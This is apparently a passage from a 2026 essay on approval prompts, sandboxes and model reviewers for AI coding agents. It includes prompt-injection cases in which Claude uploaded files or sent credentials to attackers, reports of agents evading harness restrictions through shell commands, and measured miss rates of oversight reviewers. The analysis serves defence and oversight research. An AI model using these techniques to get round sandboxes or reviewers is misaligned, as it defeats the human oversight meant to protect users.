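When an approved action does damage, the logged approval makes it look as though someone considered the action and accepted the consequences, even if they were clicking through their fortieth prompt of the afternoon or the prompt never showed what would happen.

*Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance* (2026) proposes a way to prove whether an agent's provider kept specific promises, such as getting consent before anything destructive. It examines a case in which an agent running GPT-5.6 Sol got the location of the home directory wrong and ran a deletion command that wiped it. The proposed system could require approval for that exact command, but it couldn't determine which files the command would delete or whether the user had agreed to lose each one. The consent record would therefore cover only the text of the command. For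 it to cover the deletion itself, the agent would have to use a tool that names the files.

The anthropologist Madeleine Clare Elish coined the term "moral crumple zone" for a person who takes the blame for a failure in an automated system they barely controlled. Like the part of a car that absorbs the force of a crash, the operator absorbs the blame and so protects the reputation of the system and its maker. *Don't blame me* (2026), a paper on moral responsibility in human oversight, cites Elish's work. People who approve permission prompts fit this description well. The vendor decides when the prompts appear and what they show, the employer decides how much work the approver must get through, and the log records the approver's name.

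Blaming the approver also assumes that the right answer was clear at the time. In *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026), reviewers judged whether 125 agent actions were risky, and their agreement was only moderate (a Fleiss' kappa of 0.52, where 0 is chance agreement and 1 is perfect agreement). A colleague might well have approved the same request before a disaster made the danger obvious. Some of the practitioners Salerno and colleagues interviewed also described skipping review under time pressure, which is partly their manager's responsibility.

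Approval fatigue doesn't excuse every approval. Someone who reads "delete the client archive", understands it and clicks "Yes" has made a decision. Before holding a person responsible, an investigator should find out what the prompt displayed, how long the person took to answer, how many prompts they had already handled, and how often other approvers catch similar requests. If an employer's own tests show that approvers catch only 15% of the requests they should deny, and the employer relies on them anyway, it should carry much of the responsibility when they miss one.

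An approval step can also reassure people more than it should. A speaker quoted in *EU AI Act shines light on human oversight needs*, published by IAPP, an association of privacy professionals, complained that "too many people perceive human oversight as a panacea". A company that believes someone checks every command may put off buying backups or restricting the agent's access. Users in Yan's experiment reported a high sense of control under all three permission designs, but 33 of the 35 who wrote their own standing rules approved at least one action that went beyond the task.

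### Human oversight under the EU AI Act

European law will require more than a person who clicks "Yes". Article 14 of the EU AI Act covers human oversight of high-risk AI systems, and the European Commission's *Article 14* page gives the current text. Providers must design these systems so that people can oversee them effectively while they are in use, with measures that match the system's risks, its autonomy and the setting. As far as is appropriate and proportionate, the people in charge of oversight must be able to:

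- understand what the system can and can't do, and monitor it for problems;
- stay aware of automation bias, the tendency to rely on a system's output automatically or too much;
- interpret its output correctly;
- decide not to use it, or override or reverse its output;
- interrupt it with a stop button or something similar that brings it to a safe halt.

The article doesn't mention permission prompts. A prompt could help meet the requirement that people be able to override the system, but Yue's case shows why the system also needs a working stop control. For certain systems that identify people from their faces or other biometric data, the article also requires two qualified people to verify each identification separately before anyone acts on it, with some exceptions for police, migration and border control. The second check protects against one person's lapse, but less so if both people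 are in the habit of approving.

None of this applies yet. The high-risk rules were originally due to start in August 2026, and articles written before this summer may still give that date. The European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744 of the European Parliament and of the Council* (2026) postponed them:

| Kind of high-risk system | Article 14 applies from |
|---|---|
| Uses listed in Annex III, such as recruitment and credit scoring | 2 December 2027 |
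| Products covered by Annex I, such as medical devices, and their safety components | 2 August 2028 |

Systems already on the market by then generally fall under the rules only if their design changes significantly afterwards, although high-risk systems meant for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030 even if their design doesn't change. An agent that ranks job applicants would normally count as high-risk, while an ordinary coding agent wouldn't, even if both ran on the same model and showed the same prompts.

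The duty on automation bias is weaker than it may sound, because it requires only awareness. A third of the practitioners surveyed by Salerno and colleagues already knew they had become less careful. *Automation bias in the AI Act*, a legal analysis, argues that the Act concentrates on providers and doesn't adequately address design and context as causes of the bias, and predicts that the awareness requirement will be difficult to enforce. A provider could perhaps comply by warning users about approval fatigue while still showing them hundreds of prompts. The requirement that oversight be effective is more demanding. An approval log can't show that it has been met, but a measured catch rate would be relevant evidence.

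### Why approvals can still be worth keeping

An approver with a poor catch rate can still save more time than the prompts cost. Let L be the average cost of an unwanted action that runs, and c the cost of answering one prompt. If false refusals are rare enough to ignore, the prompts are worth having when:

```
L > c / (π × h)
```

Suppose a prompt takes 10 seconds, 1% of requests for this kind of command are unwanted, and the approver catches 15% of them. The prompts save time overall if the average unwanted action would take more than about 1 hour 50 minutes to fix. If only 0.1% of requests are unwanted, the threshold rises to 18.5 hours. Recovering from a deleted production database could easily take that long, but dealing with a needless test run never would. The calculation ignores how each prompt affects attention to the next, so it is a much better argument for a few prompts on dangerous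 commands than for prompts on everything.

People do stop some harmful actions. A prompt saved the Copilot user's folder. In Yan's study, the participants who answered every prompt blocked more than half of the unwanted actions, although their job was easier than a programmer's.

People may also learn how the agent works from early approval prompts. A new user who reads the first few dozen learns which folders it touches, which commands it usually runs and what it tends to try when something fails. That makes it easier to write a narrow allow rule later or notice unusual behaviour. Experienced Claude Code users interrupt the agent more often, which fits this idea, but they may have learned what to watch for from its mistakes rather than from the prompts. A team could test this by giving some new users a week of manual approval before automatic review, starting others on automatic review immediately,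 and comparing how well the two groups later spot planted requests.

Anthropic reported that its model reviewer did as well as or better than people on every measure it tested. It still recommends that users review Claude's actions themselves when Claude makes high-stakes changes to production infrastructure.

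## Changing what is asked and who answers

If approvers have stopped reading permission requests, a team can ask them less often, ask them about something larger than a single command, or have a model approve or deny requests instead. Each option affects which requests reach a person, so the denial rate can change even if the agent behaves as before.

### Narrower rules

The easiest change is to replace broad allow rules with narrow ones, such as allowing only `npm test` instead of any `npm` command. This may raise the denial rate, as in the earlier worked example, even though fewer unwanted actions run.

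Narrow rules are hard to write because agents phrase the same operation in many ways. When Zhong and colleagues asked Codex to replace one word in a file, it wrapped the edit in a script with its own error checks. Codex then offered to stop asking about `sed -i`, which would let it edit any file in place. A rule for the whole script would probably never have matched again. Some users settle for very broad rules. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) mentions a settings file inside OpenAI that always allowed `codex exec --yolo`, which starts another Codex agent with no approvals.

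Rules that forbid actions have gaps for the same reason. In 77 of the 290 reports that Zhong and colleagues studied, shell commands bypassed restrictions that the harness applied only to its built-in file tools. For example, an agent that couldn't open a file with the built-in reader could print it with `cat`.

Software can also choose the permissions for each task, but it sometimes withholds ones the task needs. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) compared two models that predict which permissions a task needs. One removed at least one necessary permission in 21% of tasks, and the other in 11%. Those tasks would fail unless the harness asked the user for the missing permission, which would bring back some of the prompts.

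### Sandboxes

A sandbox limits what a command can reach, so the harness doesn't have to guess this from the command's text. Claude Code's sandbox lets commands read files and write inside the workspace, and it blocks network access by default. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%. In an illustrative snapshot of OpenAI's internal use of Codex, 9,280 of 10,000 actions stayed inside the sandbox and the other 720 needed approval.

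An 84% reduction would leave 320 prompts for the team that answered 2,000 and denied 70. If denials fell in proportion, the denial rate would stay at 3.5%. But if half the denied requests had involved the network or files outside the project, those 35 denials would remain and the rate would rise to 10.9%.

Sandboxes also interfere with legitimate work, such as test suites and builds. They contributed to 41 of the 290 reports, either by blocking such work or by failing to protect the files inside them. Many harnesses offer to rerun a failed command without the sandbox, and Zhong and colleagues found that repeated offers lead users to turn the sandbox off entirely.

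According to Anthropic's *sandbox environments*, Claude Code's built-in sandbox restricts only shell commands. The file tools, hooks and MCP servers (separate programs that give the agent extra tools) still run directly on the user's machine. Running all of Claude Code in a container or virtual machine restricts those too. Even then, the agent can damage any project files it can write to, and if it has network access, it can leak anything it can read.

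A list of approved network addresses doesn't fully prevent leaks. Claude Cowork's sandbox had to allow traffic to Anthropic's own servers. Someone reported an attack in which a file in the workspace contained hidden instructions and the attacker's access key. Claude followed the instructions and uploaded the user's other files to the attacker's Anthropic account, which the sandbox allowed because all the traffic went to an approved address. Anthropic now checks that each request carries the session's own credentials.

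### Approving a plan or a finished result

Users reject 39% of plan approval requests. Plan approval works well for disagreements about approach, such as whether to start on a new branch. But a plan describes what the agent intends to do, and "run the database migration" reads the same whether or not the migration also drops a table. There seems to be no published experiment in which researchers planted a dangerous step in a plan and counted how many people noticed.

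Staging postpones the decision until the changes are visible. Zhong and colleagues built a filesystem called YoloFS that sits between the agent and the user's real files:

1. When the agent changes a file, YoloFS saves the new version separately and leaves the original alone. The agent sees the new version and carries on.
2. After each command, YoloFS takes a snapshot and shows the agent which files changed. The agent can return to an earlier snapshot if something looks wrong.
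3. At the end, the user reviews the combined changes and commits or discards them. The agent can't commit its own work.

Staging can't undo an agent reading a secret, so YoloFS prompts the user before the agent opens a sensitive file. The prompt names the file, such as the user's SSH key, and the answer can become a rule that applies to any command that tries to open that file. If nobody answers in time, YoloFS denies access.

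Zhong and colleagues tested Claude Code with and without YoloFS on 11 tasks in which a routine command did hidden damage, and on 112 simple file operations:

| | With YoloFS | Without it |
|---|---|---|
| Hidden damage (11 tasks) | The agent undid it in 8; in the other 3 it stayed staged | Damage in 10; the agent asked the user in 1 |
| Success on routine tasks | 99% | 98% |
| Times a routine task had to wait for the user | 0.4 on average | 0.9 on average |

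In one of the eight tasks, a supposed code formatter rewrote two source files and deleted two documents. Claude saw the list of changes, restored the snapshot and read the script. In one of the other three, a deployment script copied the source code to a new folder and deleted the original. Claude noticed the deletion but took it to be a normal part of deployment. The user could still have rejected that change, but no people took part in the test, so we don't know whether they would have. Someone facing a long list of changes late in the day may also approve it without reading it.

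The 0.4 average also leaves out the final review. Nearly all the reduction came from work inside the project, where YoloFS never asked for permission. For files outside the project, the average was 0.9 with YoloFS and 1.1 without it. Codex also averaged 0.4 with its ordinary sandbox.

In an outside test, the agent often failed to undo the damage. Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Shall We Approve?*, extended the hidden-damage tasks to 102 cases and used a different model as the agent. Harm occurred in 71.6% of tasks without any approval and in 35.3% with YoloFS. The agent restored an earlier state in 66 of the YoloFS runs. It did not do so in the other 36, and 33 of those ended in harm. These figures appear to leave out final review by a person, which might have prevented some of the harm.

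With staging, the log no longer contains denials inside the project. Instead, it contains refusals to open a named file and rejected sets of changes. A refusal to open a file is easier to interpret than a refused command because the user has objected to that particular access. Rejecting a set of changes is closer to a code review because the user has already seen the result.

### Predicting the user's answer

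A harness could also learn to answer as the user would. Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, showed 205 people imaginary situations in which an assistant would share their data with a tool, for instance to book a flight. Their predictor combines a language model, given the person's earlier decisions, with a method based on what similar people chose. It was right 85.1% of the time overall, and 94.4% of the time when it answered only high-confidence cases, though this left many requests without a prediction.

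These decisions were about sharing data, not running shell commands. Accuracy would also be a misleading measure for Claude Code, because its users approve 97% of prompts. A program that always answered "allow" would be 97% accurate without blocking anything. A useful test would report the predictor's catch rate and false refusal rate.

A more basic objection is that users may have approved past requests because they were tired. *Hedwig* (2026), a system that adjusts a coding agent's independence to its user, was tested on simulated users with different habits. One approved 95% of requests, and *Hedwig* inferred that this user wanted fewer check-ins. It then skipped the plan review for low-risk plans, although signs of serious risk could still trigger one. *Hedwig* would infer the same about a tired user who approved just as often.

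The predictor would also reduce its own supply of evidence, because users don't see the requests it answers. They may never correct a mistaken preference it learned in the first week. A team could limit this by training the predictor only on decisions from people who catch planted requests, and by still asking users about a random sample of the requests it would allow.

### How Claude Code's model reviewer decides

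A model reviewer judges whether an action is acceptable, rather than whether this user would probably click "Yes". In Claude Code's auto mode, an action goes through up to three steps:

1. **Exempt actions run at once.** These are read-only tools, edits inside the project and commands that match a narrow allow rule.
2. **A fast filter checks the rest.** The model answers yes or no without reasoning, and its instructions tell it to block if in doubt. Actions that pass can run.
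3. **A slower check looks again at whatever the filter flagged.** The model sees the same material but reasons about it before making the final decision.

The reviewer reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that they can't sway the reviewer toward a bad decision, and the results of tool calls because a web page or file may contain an attacker's instructions. Without this text, if the agent cancels "job abc123" and the user never mentioned that number, the reviewer can't tell whether the agent looked it up or invented it. But when Anthropic put the text back, the reviewer did worse on real cases of overreach. When the reviewer saw only the tool calls and not the user's messages, it missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked some that users had plainly requested.

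In March 2026 Anthropic published these error rates:

| | Ordinary actions blocked (of 10,000) | Real overeager actions missed (of 52) | Synthetic data leaks missed (of 1,000) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast filter alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Filter and slower check | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The slower check removes about 95% of the mistaken blocks, but it also lets through some dangerous actions that the filter had caught. Anthropic accepted this tradeoff because users would be unlikely to tolerate a reviewer that blocked one in 12 ordinary actions. The 17% miss rate is based on about nine misses in 52 cases, so the true rate for similar cases could be from about 9% to 30%.

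In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised that the action was dangerous but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a user says "clean up the PR", meaning a pull request, and the agent force-pushes, which overwrites the branch's history. The user asked for a clean-up but never mentioned overwriting anything. In other cases, the reviewer treated approval of one action as permission for a similar one. Anthropic tried to fix this by changing the reviewer's instructions, but every change it tried did more harm than good.

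Models can judge permission well when it is spelled out. *Same Operation, Different Permission* (Jing, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tested eight automated reviewers on the same operations with and without valid authorisation, and two judged all 160 cases correctly. Users can therefore help the reviewer by naming the target and the limit, as in "tidy the pull request's description, but don't push anything".

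### What other tests found

Ji and colleagues ran the first independent evaluation of auto mode, using AmPermBench, their benchmark of ambiguous requests. They examined 253 actions that changed files or other system state. Auto mode missed 81.0% of the actions it should have stopped. The reviewer never saw 36.8% of the 253 actions because they were file edits inside the project. For example, when a command-line tool wasn't available, agents got the same effect by editing the file that stored the system's state.

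Among the 160 actions that the reviewer did see, it blocked 29.7% of the unwanted ones (missing 70.3%) and 31.9% of the acceptable ones, so a block on these tasks was no evidence that anything was wrong. Ji and colleagues stress that the benchmark differs greatly from ordinary use, so the results don't contradict Anthropic's 17%. The results also date from April, before Anthropic's later improvements.

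Some of those improvements came from Apollo Research's synthetic attacks. Anthropic responded to them by giving the reviewer more context, such as whether a repository was public. Apollo then retested the reviewer on attacks Anthropic had never seen. It caught about half of those it had previously missed, and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. Across all the attacks, including those Apollo had shared with Anthropic, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. The results on unseen attacks are better evidence of a general improvement, because Anthropic couldn't have tailored its changes to them. Anthropic says the attacks were more malicious than anything Claude would do unprompted, so 7% isn't the miss rate in normal use.

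More context doesn't help if the text of a command doesn't show what it will do, as with `cargo build`. Wu, Chen and colleagues built a system called Caper that runs each command in an isolated copy of the environment and gives a model a short report of what changed. If the model rejects the changes, Caper restores the earlier state.

They tested Caper and auto mode on two sets of tasks. The first came from SABER, a benchmark in which a reasonable request can lead to harm, and the second was their extended set of hidden-damage tasks. The table shows the share of tasks that ended in harm:

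| | SABER (682 tasks) | Hidden damage (102 tasks) |
|---|---|---|
| No approval | 19.7% | 71.6% |
| Auto mode | 14.8% | 62.7% |
| Caper, running inside Claude Code | 10.0% | 6.9% |

The researchers ran auto mode with an OpenAI model as the reviewer and a third company's model as the agent, so these aren't the error rates of Anthropic's models. They also designed both Caper and the hidden-damage tasks. Still, they used the same two models to compare auto mode and Caper, which suggests that the report caused the difference in results.

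A further test supports this, using a harmless twin of each of the 102 tasks with the same request and command. Caper's reviewer blocked 61.8% of the twins without the report and only 1.0% with it. The sandbox added about half a second to each allowed command. Caper can't undo anything that leaves the isolated copy, so it blocks outside connections. A malicious program could also detect the test environment and delay its harmful actions.

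### Codex's Auto-review

OpenAI's Auto-review reviews only requests to leave the sandbox. In the snapshot of 10,000 actions, it approved 713 of 720 requests and denied 7. After four of the denials, the agent found a safer way to continue. After the other three, it stopped and asked the user, so people had to answer 3 questions instead of 720.

OpenAI reports that Auto-review denied 90.3% of synthetic overeager actions. Anthropic's reviewer caught 83%, but the two figures aren't comparable because Anthropic used real cases. OpenAI also reports that Auto-review approved 99.1% of real requests to leave the sandbox that users had approved. Tired users may have approved some requests they didn't want, so some of the 0.9% that Auto-review refused may have been correct refusals.

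Trębacz and colleagues report that people and models misled Auto-review into approving commands during testing, and that it doesn't review actions that stay inside the sandbox. It therefore wouldn't catch an agent deleting the wrong project file there.

One commissioned test compared the two companies' products on hidden instructions in web pages and other content. Trajectory Labs ran 720 attacks against each model for Anthropic:

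| | Attacks that succeeded with a model reviewer | Without one |
|---|---|---|
| Claude models in Claude Code | 0% | 0.09% on average |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex | 5.83% | 19.03% |

Claude models resisted almost every attack even in bypass mode, so the test is a poor measure of how much protection auto mode adds. Auto-review made a bigger difference, cutting successful attacks by more than two-thirds. OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published the results, so the Codex figures may be out of date.

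### The spread of auto mode and its critics

Anthropic began making auto mode the default in Claude Code on its Pro, Max and Team plans on 14 August 2026. It has since extended the default to every plan, according to *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026). In October, Anthropic announced the same default for most of its other Claude apps on the Pro, Max and Team plans.

Willison, a software developer who writes about AI tools, agrees that auto mode is better than constant approvals, but points out that it missed 11% of the dangerous commands in Anthropic's study. He wants more independent evidence about malicious instructions. His example is a software package whose documentation tells the agent to use a second package to download some files before running the tests. The second package steals the user's data. He prefers to limit what an agent can reach. Crosley's *Claude Code Auto Mode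 Is Not a Security Boundary* likewise argues for relying on isolation and network controls.

In an exercise at Anthropic in February 2026, a researcher tricked an employee into starting Claude Code with a prompt that looked routine but included an instruction to send cloud credentials to an outside address. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 runs. A reviewer that checks for the user's consent would have found it, because the employee had entered the instruction. Anthropic has since told the reviewer never to approve sending secrets outside, even on request, which should help. A sandbox that keeps Claude from reading the credentials would protect them even if the reviewer missed the attempt.

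Michael and Roesner found that commercial agents often make users choose between constant prompts and a reviewer whose decisions they can barely see or control. None of the 21 research proposals they surveyed fully combined low user effort, precisely defined rules and predictable enforcement.

In its March article, Anthropic advised manual review of high-stakes production changes and said that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for anyone who already checks every action carefully. Some users set similar limits. *Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026), an article written for Anthropic about satisfied customers, describes an engineer at the software company Gusto who checks each tool call when working on live systems. Another engineer, at the health company Garner Health, doesn't let auto mode approve emails or Slack messages.

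### Reading the new log

Model refusals, the actions that the model reviewer blocks, belong in a separate series from people's denials because the reviewer receives different requests and has its own catch rate and false refusal rate.

Suppose the team from the earlier examples switches to auto mode. Its agent takes 10,000 actions in a month, of which 7,000 are exempt and 3,000 go to the reviewer. If 30 of those 3,000 are unwanted and Anthropic's March error rates apply, the reviewer blocks about 25 of the 30, plus 12 acceptable actions. Five requests still reach a person, who denies two.

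| Series | Count | Rate |
|---|---|---|
| People's denials before the switch | 70 of 2,000 | 3.5% |
| Model refusals | 37 of 3,000 | 1.2% |
| People's denials after the switch | 2 of 5 | 40% |

People now answer only a few unusual requests, so a chart that joined the first and last rows would wrongly show the agent getting more than ten times worse. Joining the first two rows would suggest a big improvement, which would be equally unjustified. A report should end the old series on the day of the switch and start two new ones.

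In this example, about two-thirds of the model's refusals are correct. If 1% of requests were still unwanted, but people caught 13.6% of those and refused 2% of acceptable ones, only 6% of their denials would be correct. So a model's refusal can be much better evidence of an agent failure than a person's denial. But if only 3 of the 3,000 actions were unwanted, just 17% of the model's refusals would be correct. And if the team's instructions were as vague as those in AmPermBench, the refusals might provide no information about whether an action was unwanted.

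Sometimes the reviewer blocks an action without judging it. Jing and colleagues asked two models to give a decision along with their findings and evidence. The smaller model gave no usable decision in 117 to 124 of 160 cases, depending on the run, and the system blocked the action every time. In an earlier run, this format and a stricter one both stopped all 80 forbidden actions, but this format let through only 10 of the 80 permitted actions, while the stricter one let through 71. Failed reviews need a separate count, because a log that recorded only "blocked" would make the faulty reviewer look more vigilant.

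Adding a second reviewer can be similarly misleading. In another of their tests, the second reviewer removed the first reviewer's only wrong approval but also blocked 171 permitted requests out of 767.

Refusal rates also depend on the denominator. At Gusto, about 10% of sessions contained a model refusal, while OpenAI's snapshot had 7 refusals in 10,000 actions. These could describe almost the same rate, because at 7 refusals per 10,000 actions, a session of 150 actions has a 10% chance of containing at least one.

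Overrides are a good way to find mistaken refusals. In Codex, a user can choose a recently denied action and approve it for one retry. OpenAI says the reviewer receives the user's approval but checks the action again and can still refuse it. Codex keeps only the 10 most recent denials in each thread, so a team that wants to study them would need to save them elsewhere. An override doesn't prove that the reviewer was wrong, because the user may be impatient. Mistaken refusals that users accept also don't show up as overrides.

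The reviewer's wrong approvals are harder to find than its wrong denials. The team should read a random sample of allowed actions and regularly test the reviewer on cases with known answers. Unlike a person, the reviewer can judge hundreds of cases in an afternoon without getting tired. The team should rerun the same cases after every update, because a new version can change both error rates.

### Sorting ten actions

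One way to decide who should answer a permission request is by whether the action can be undone and how far its effects reach. The table applies these two criteria to ten actions by a coding agent. The last column gives invented frequencies per 1,000 actions.

| Action | Can someone undo it? | Reach | Who decides | Per 1,000 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read a source file | Nothing to undo | Project | Nobody; it runs | 450 |
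| Edit a file saved in Git | Easily | Project | Nobody; the user reviews the finished work | 300 |
| Run the tests | Usually | Project, if sandboxed | A narrow allow rule | 150 |
| Delete the build folder | Yes, by building again | Project | Nobody, inside the sandbox | 20 |
| Overwrite a file that Git doesn't track | Only with a copy | Project | The user, after staging | 20 |
| Install a new package | Partly | The machine and the network | Model reviewer | 15 |
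| Push to the agent's own branch | Mostly | The team | Model reviewer | 30 |
| Read an SSH key | No | Every system the key opens | Nobody; the sandbox blocks it | 1 |
| Email a client | No | People outside the company | The user, at a prompt | 9 |
| Change the production database | Perhaps not | Customers | The user, at a prompt | 5 |

In 1,000 actions, the user answers 14 prompts and the model reviewer checks 45. In Claude Code's Manual mode, most of the 550 actions that don't read source files would prompt the user. Staging adds some work at the end, since the user still has to look at the 20 overwritten files and the ordinary edits.

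Changing the environment can move an action to a different row. Tests that can reach a shared database shouldn't run under an allow rule, but they can if they use a disposable copy. A push that automatically publishes the website reaches customers, so a person should approve it. A package installer that could read the user's passwords should run in a container, whatever the model reviewer decides.

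Fewer prompts won't guarantee careful answers. No published experiment has measured how well people judge a handful of serious requests after software has removed the routine ones, so the team should test this with planted requests. The team can also improve the prompts. For an email, the prompt should show the recipient, the full text and any attachments. For a database change, the harness can first run the command on a copy of the database and show which tables would lose data.
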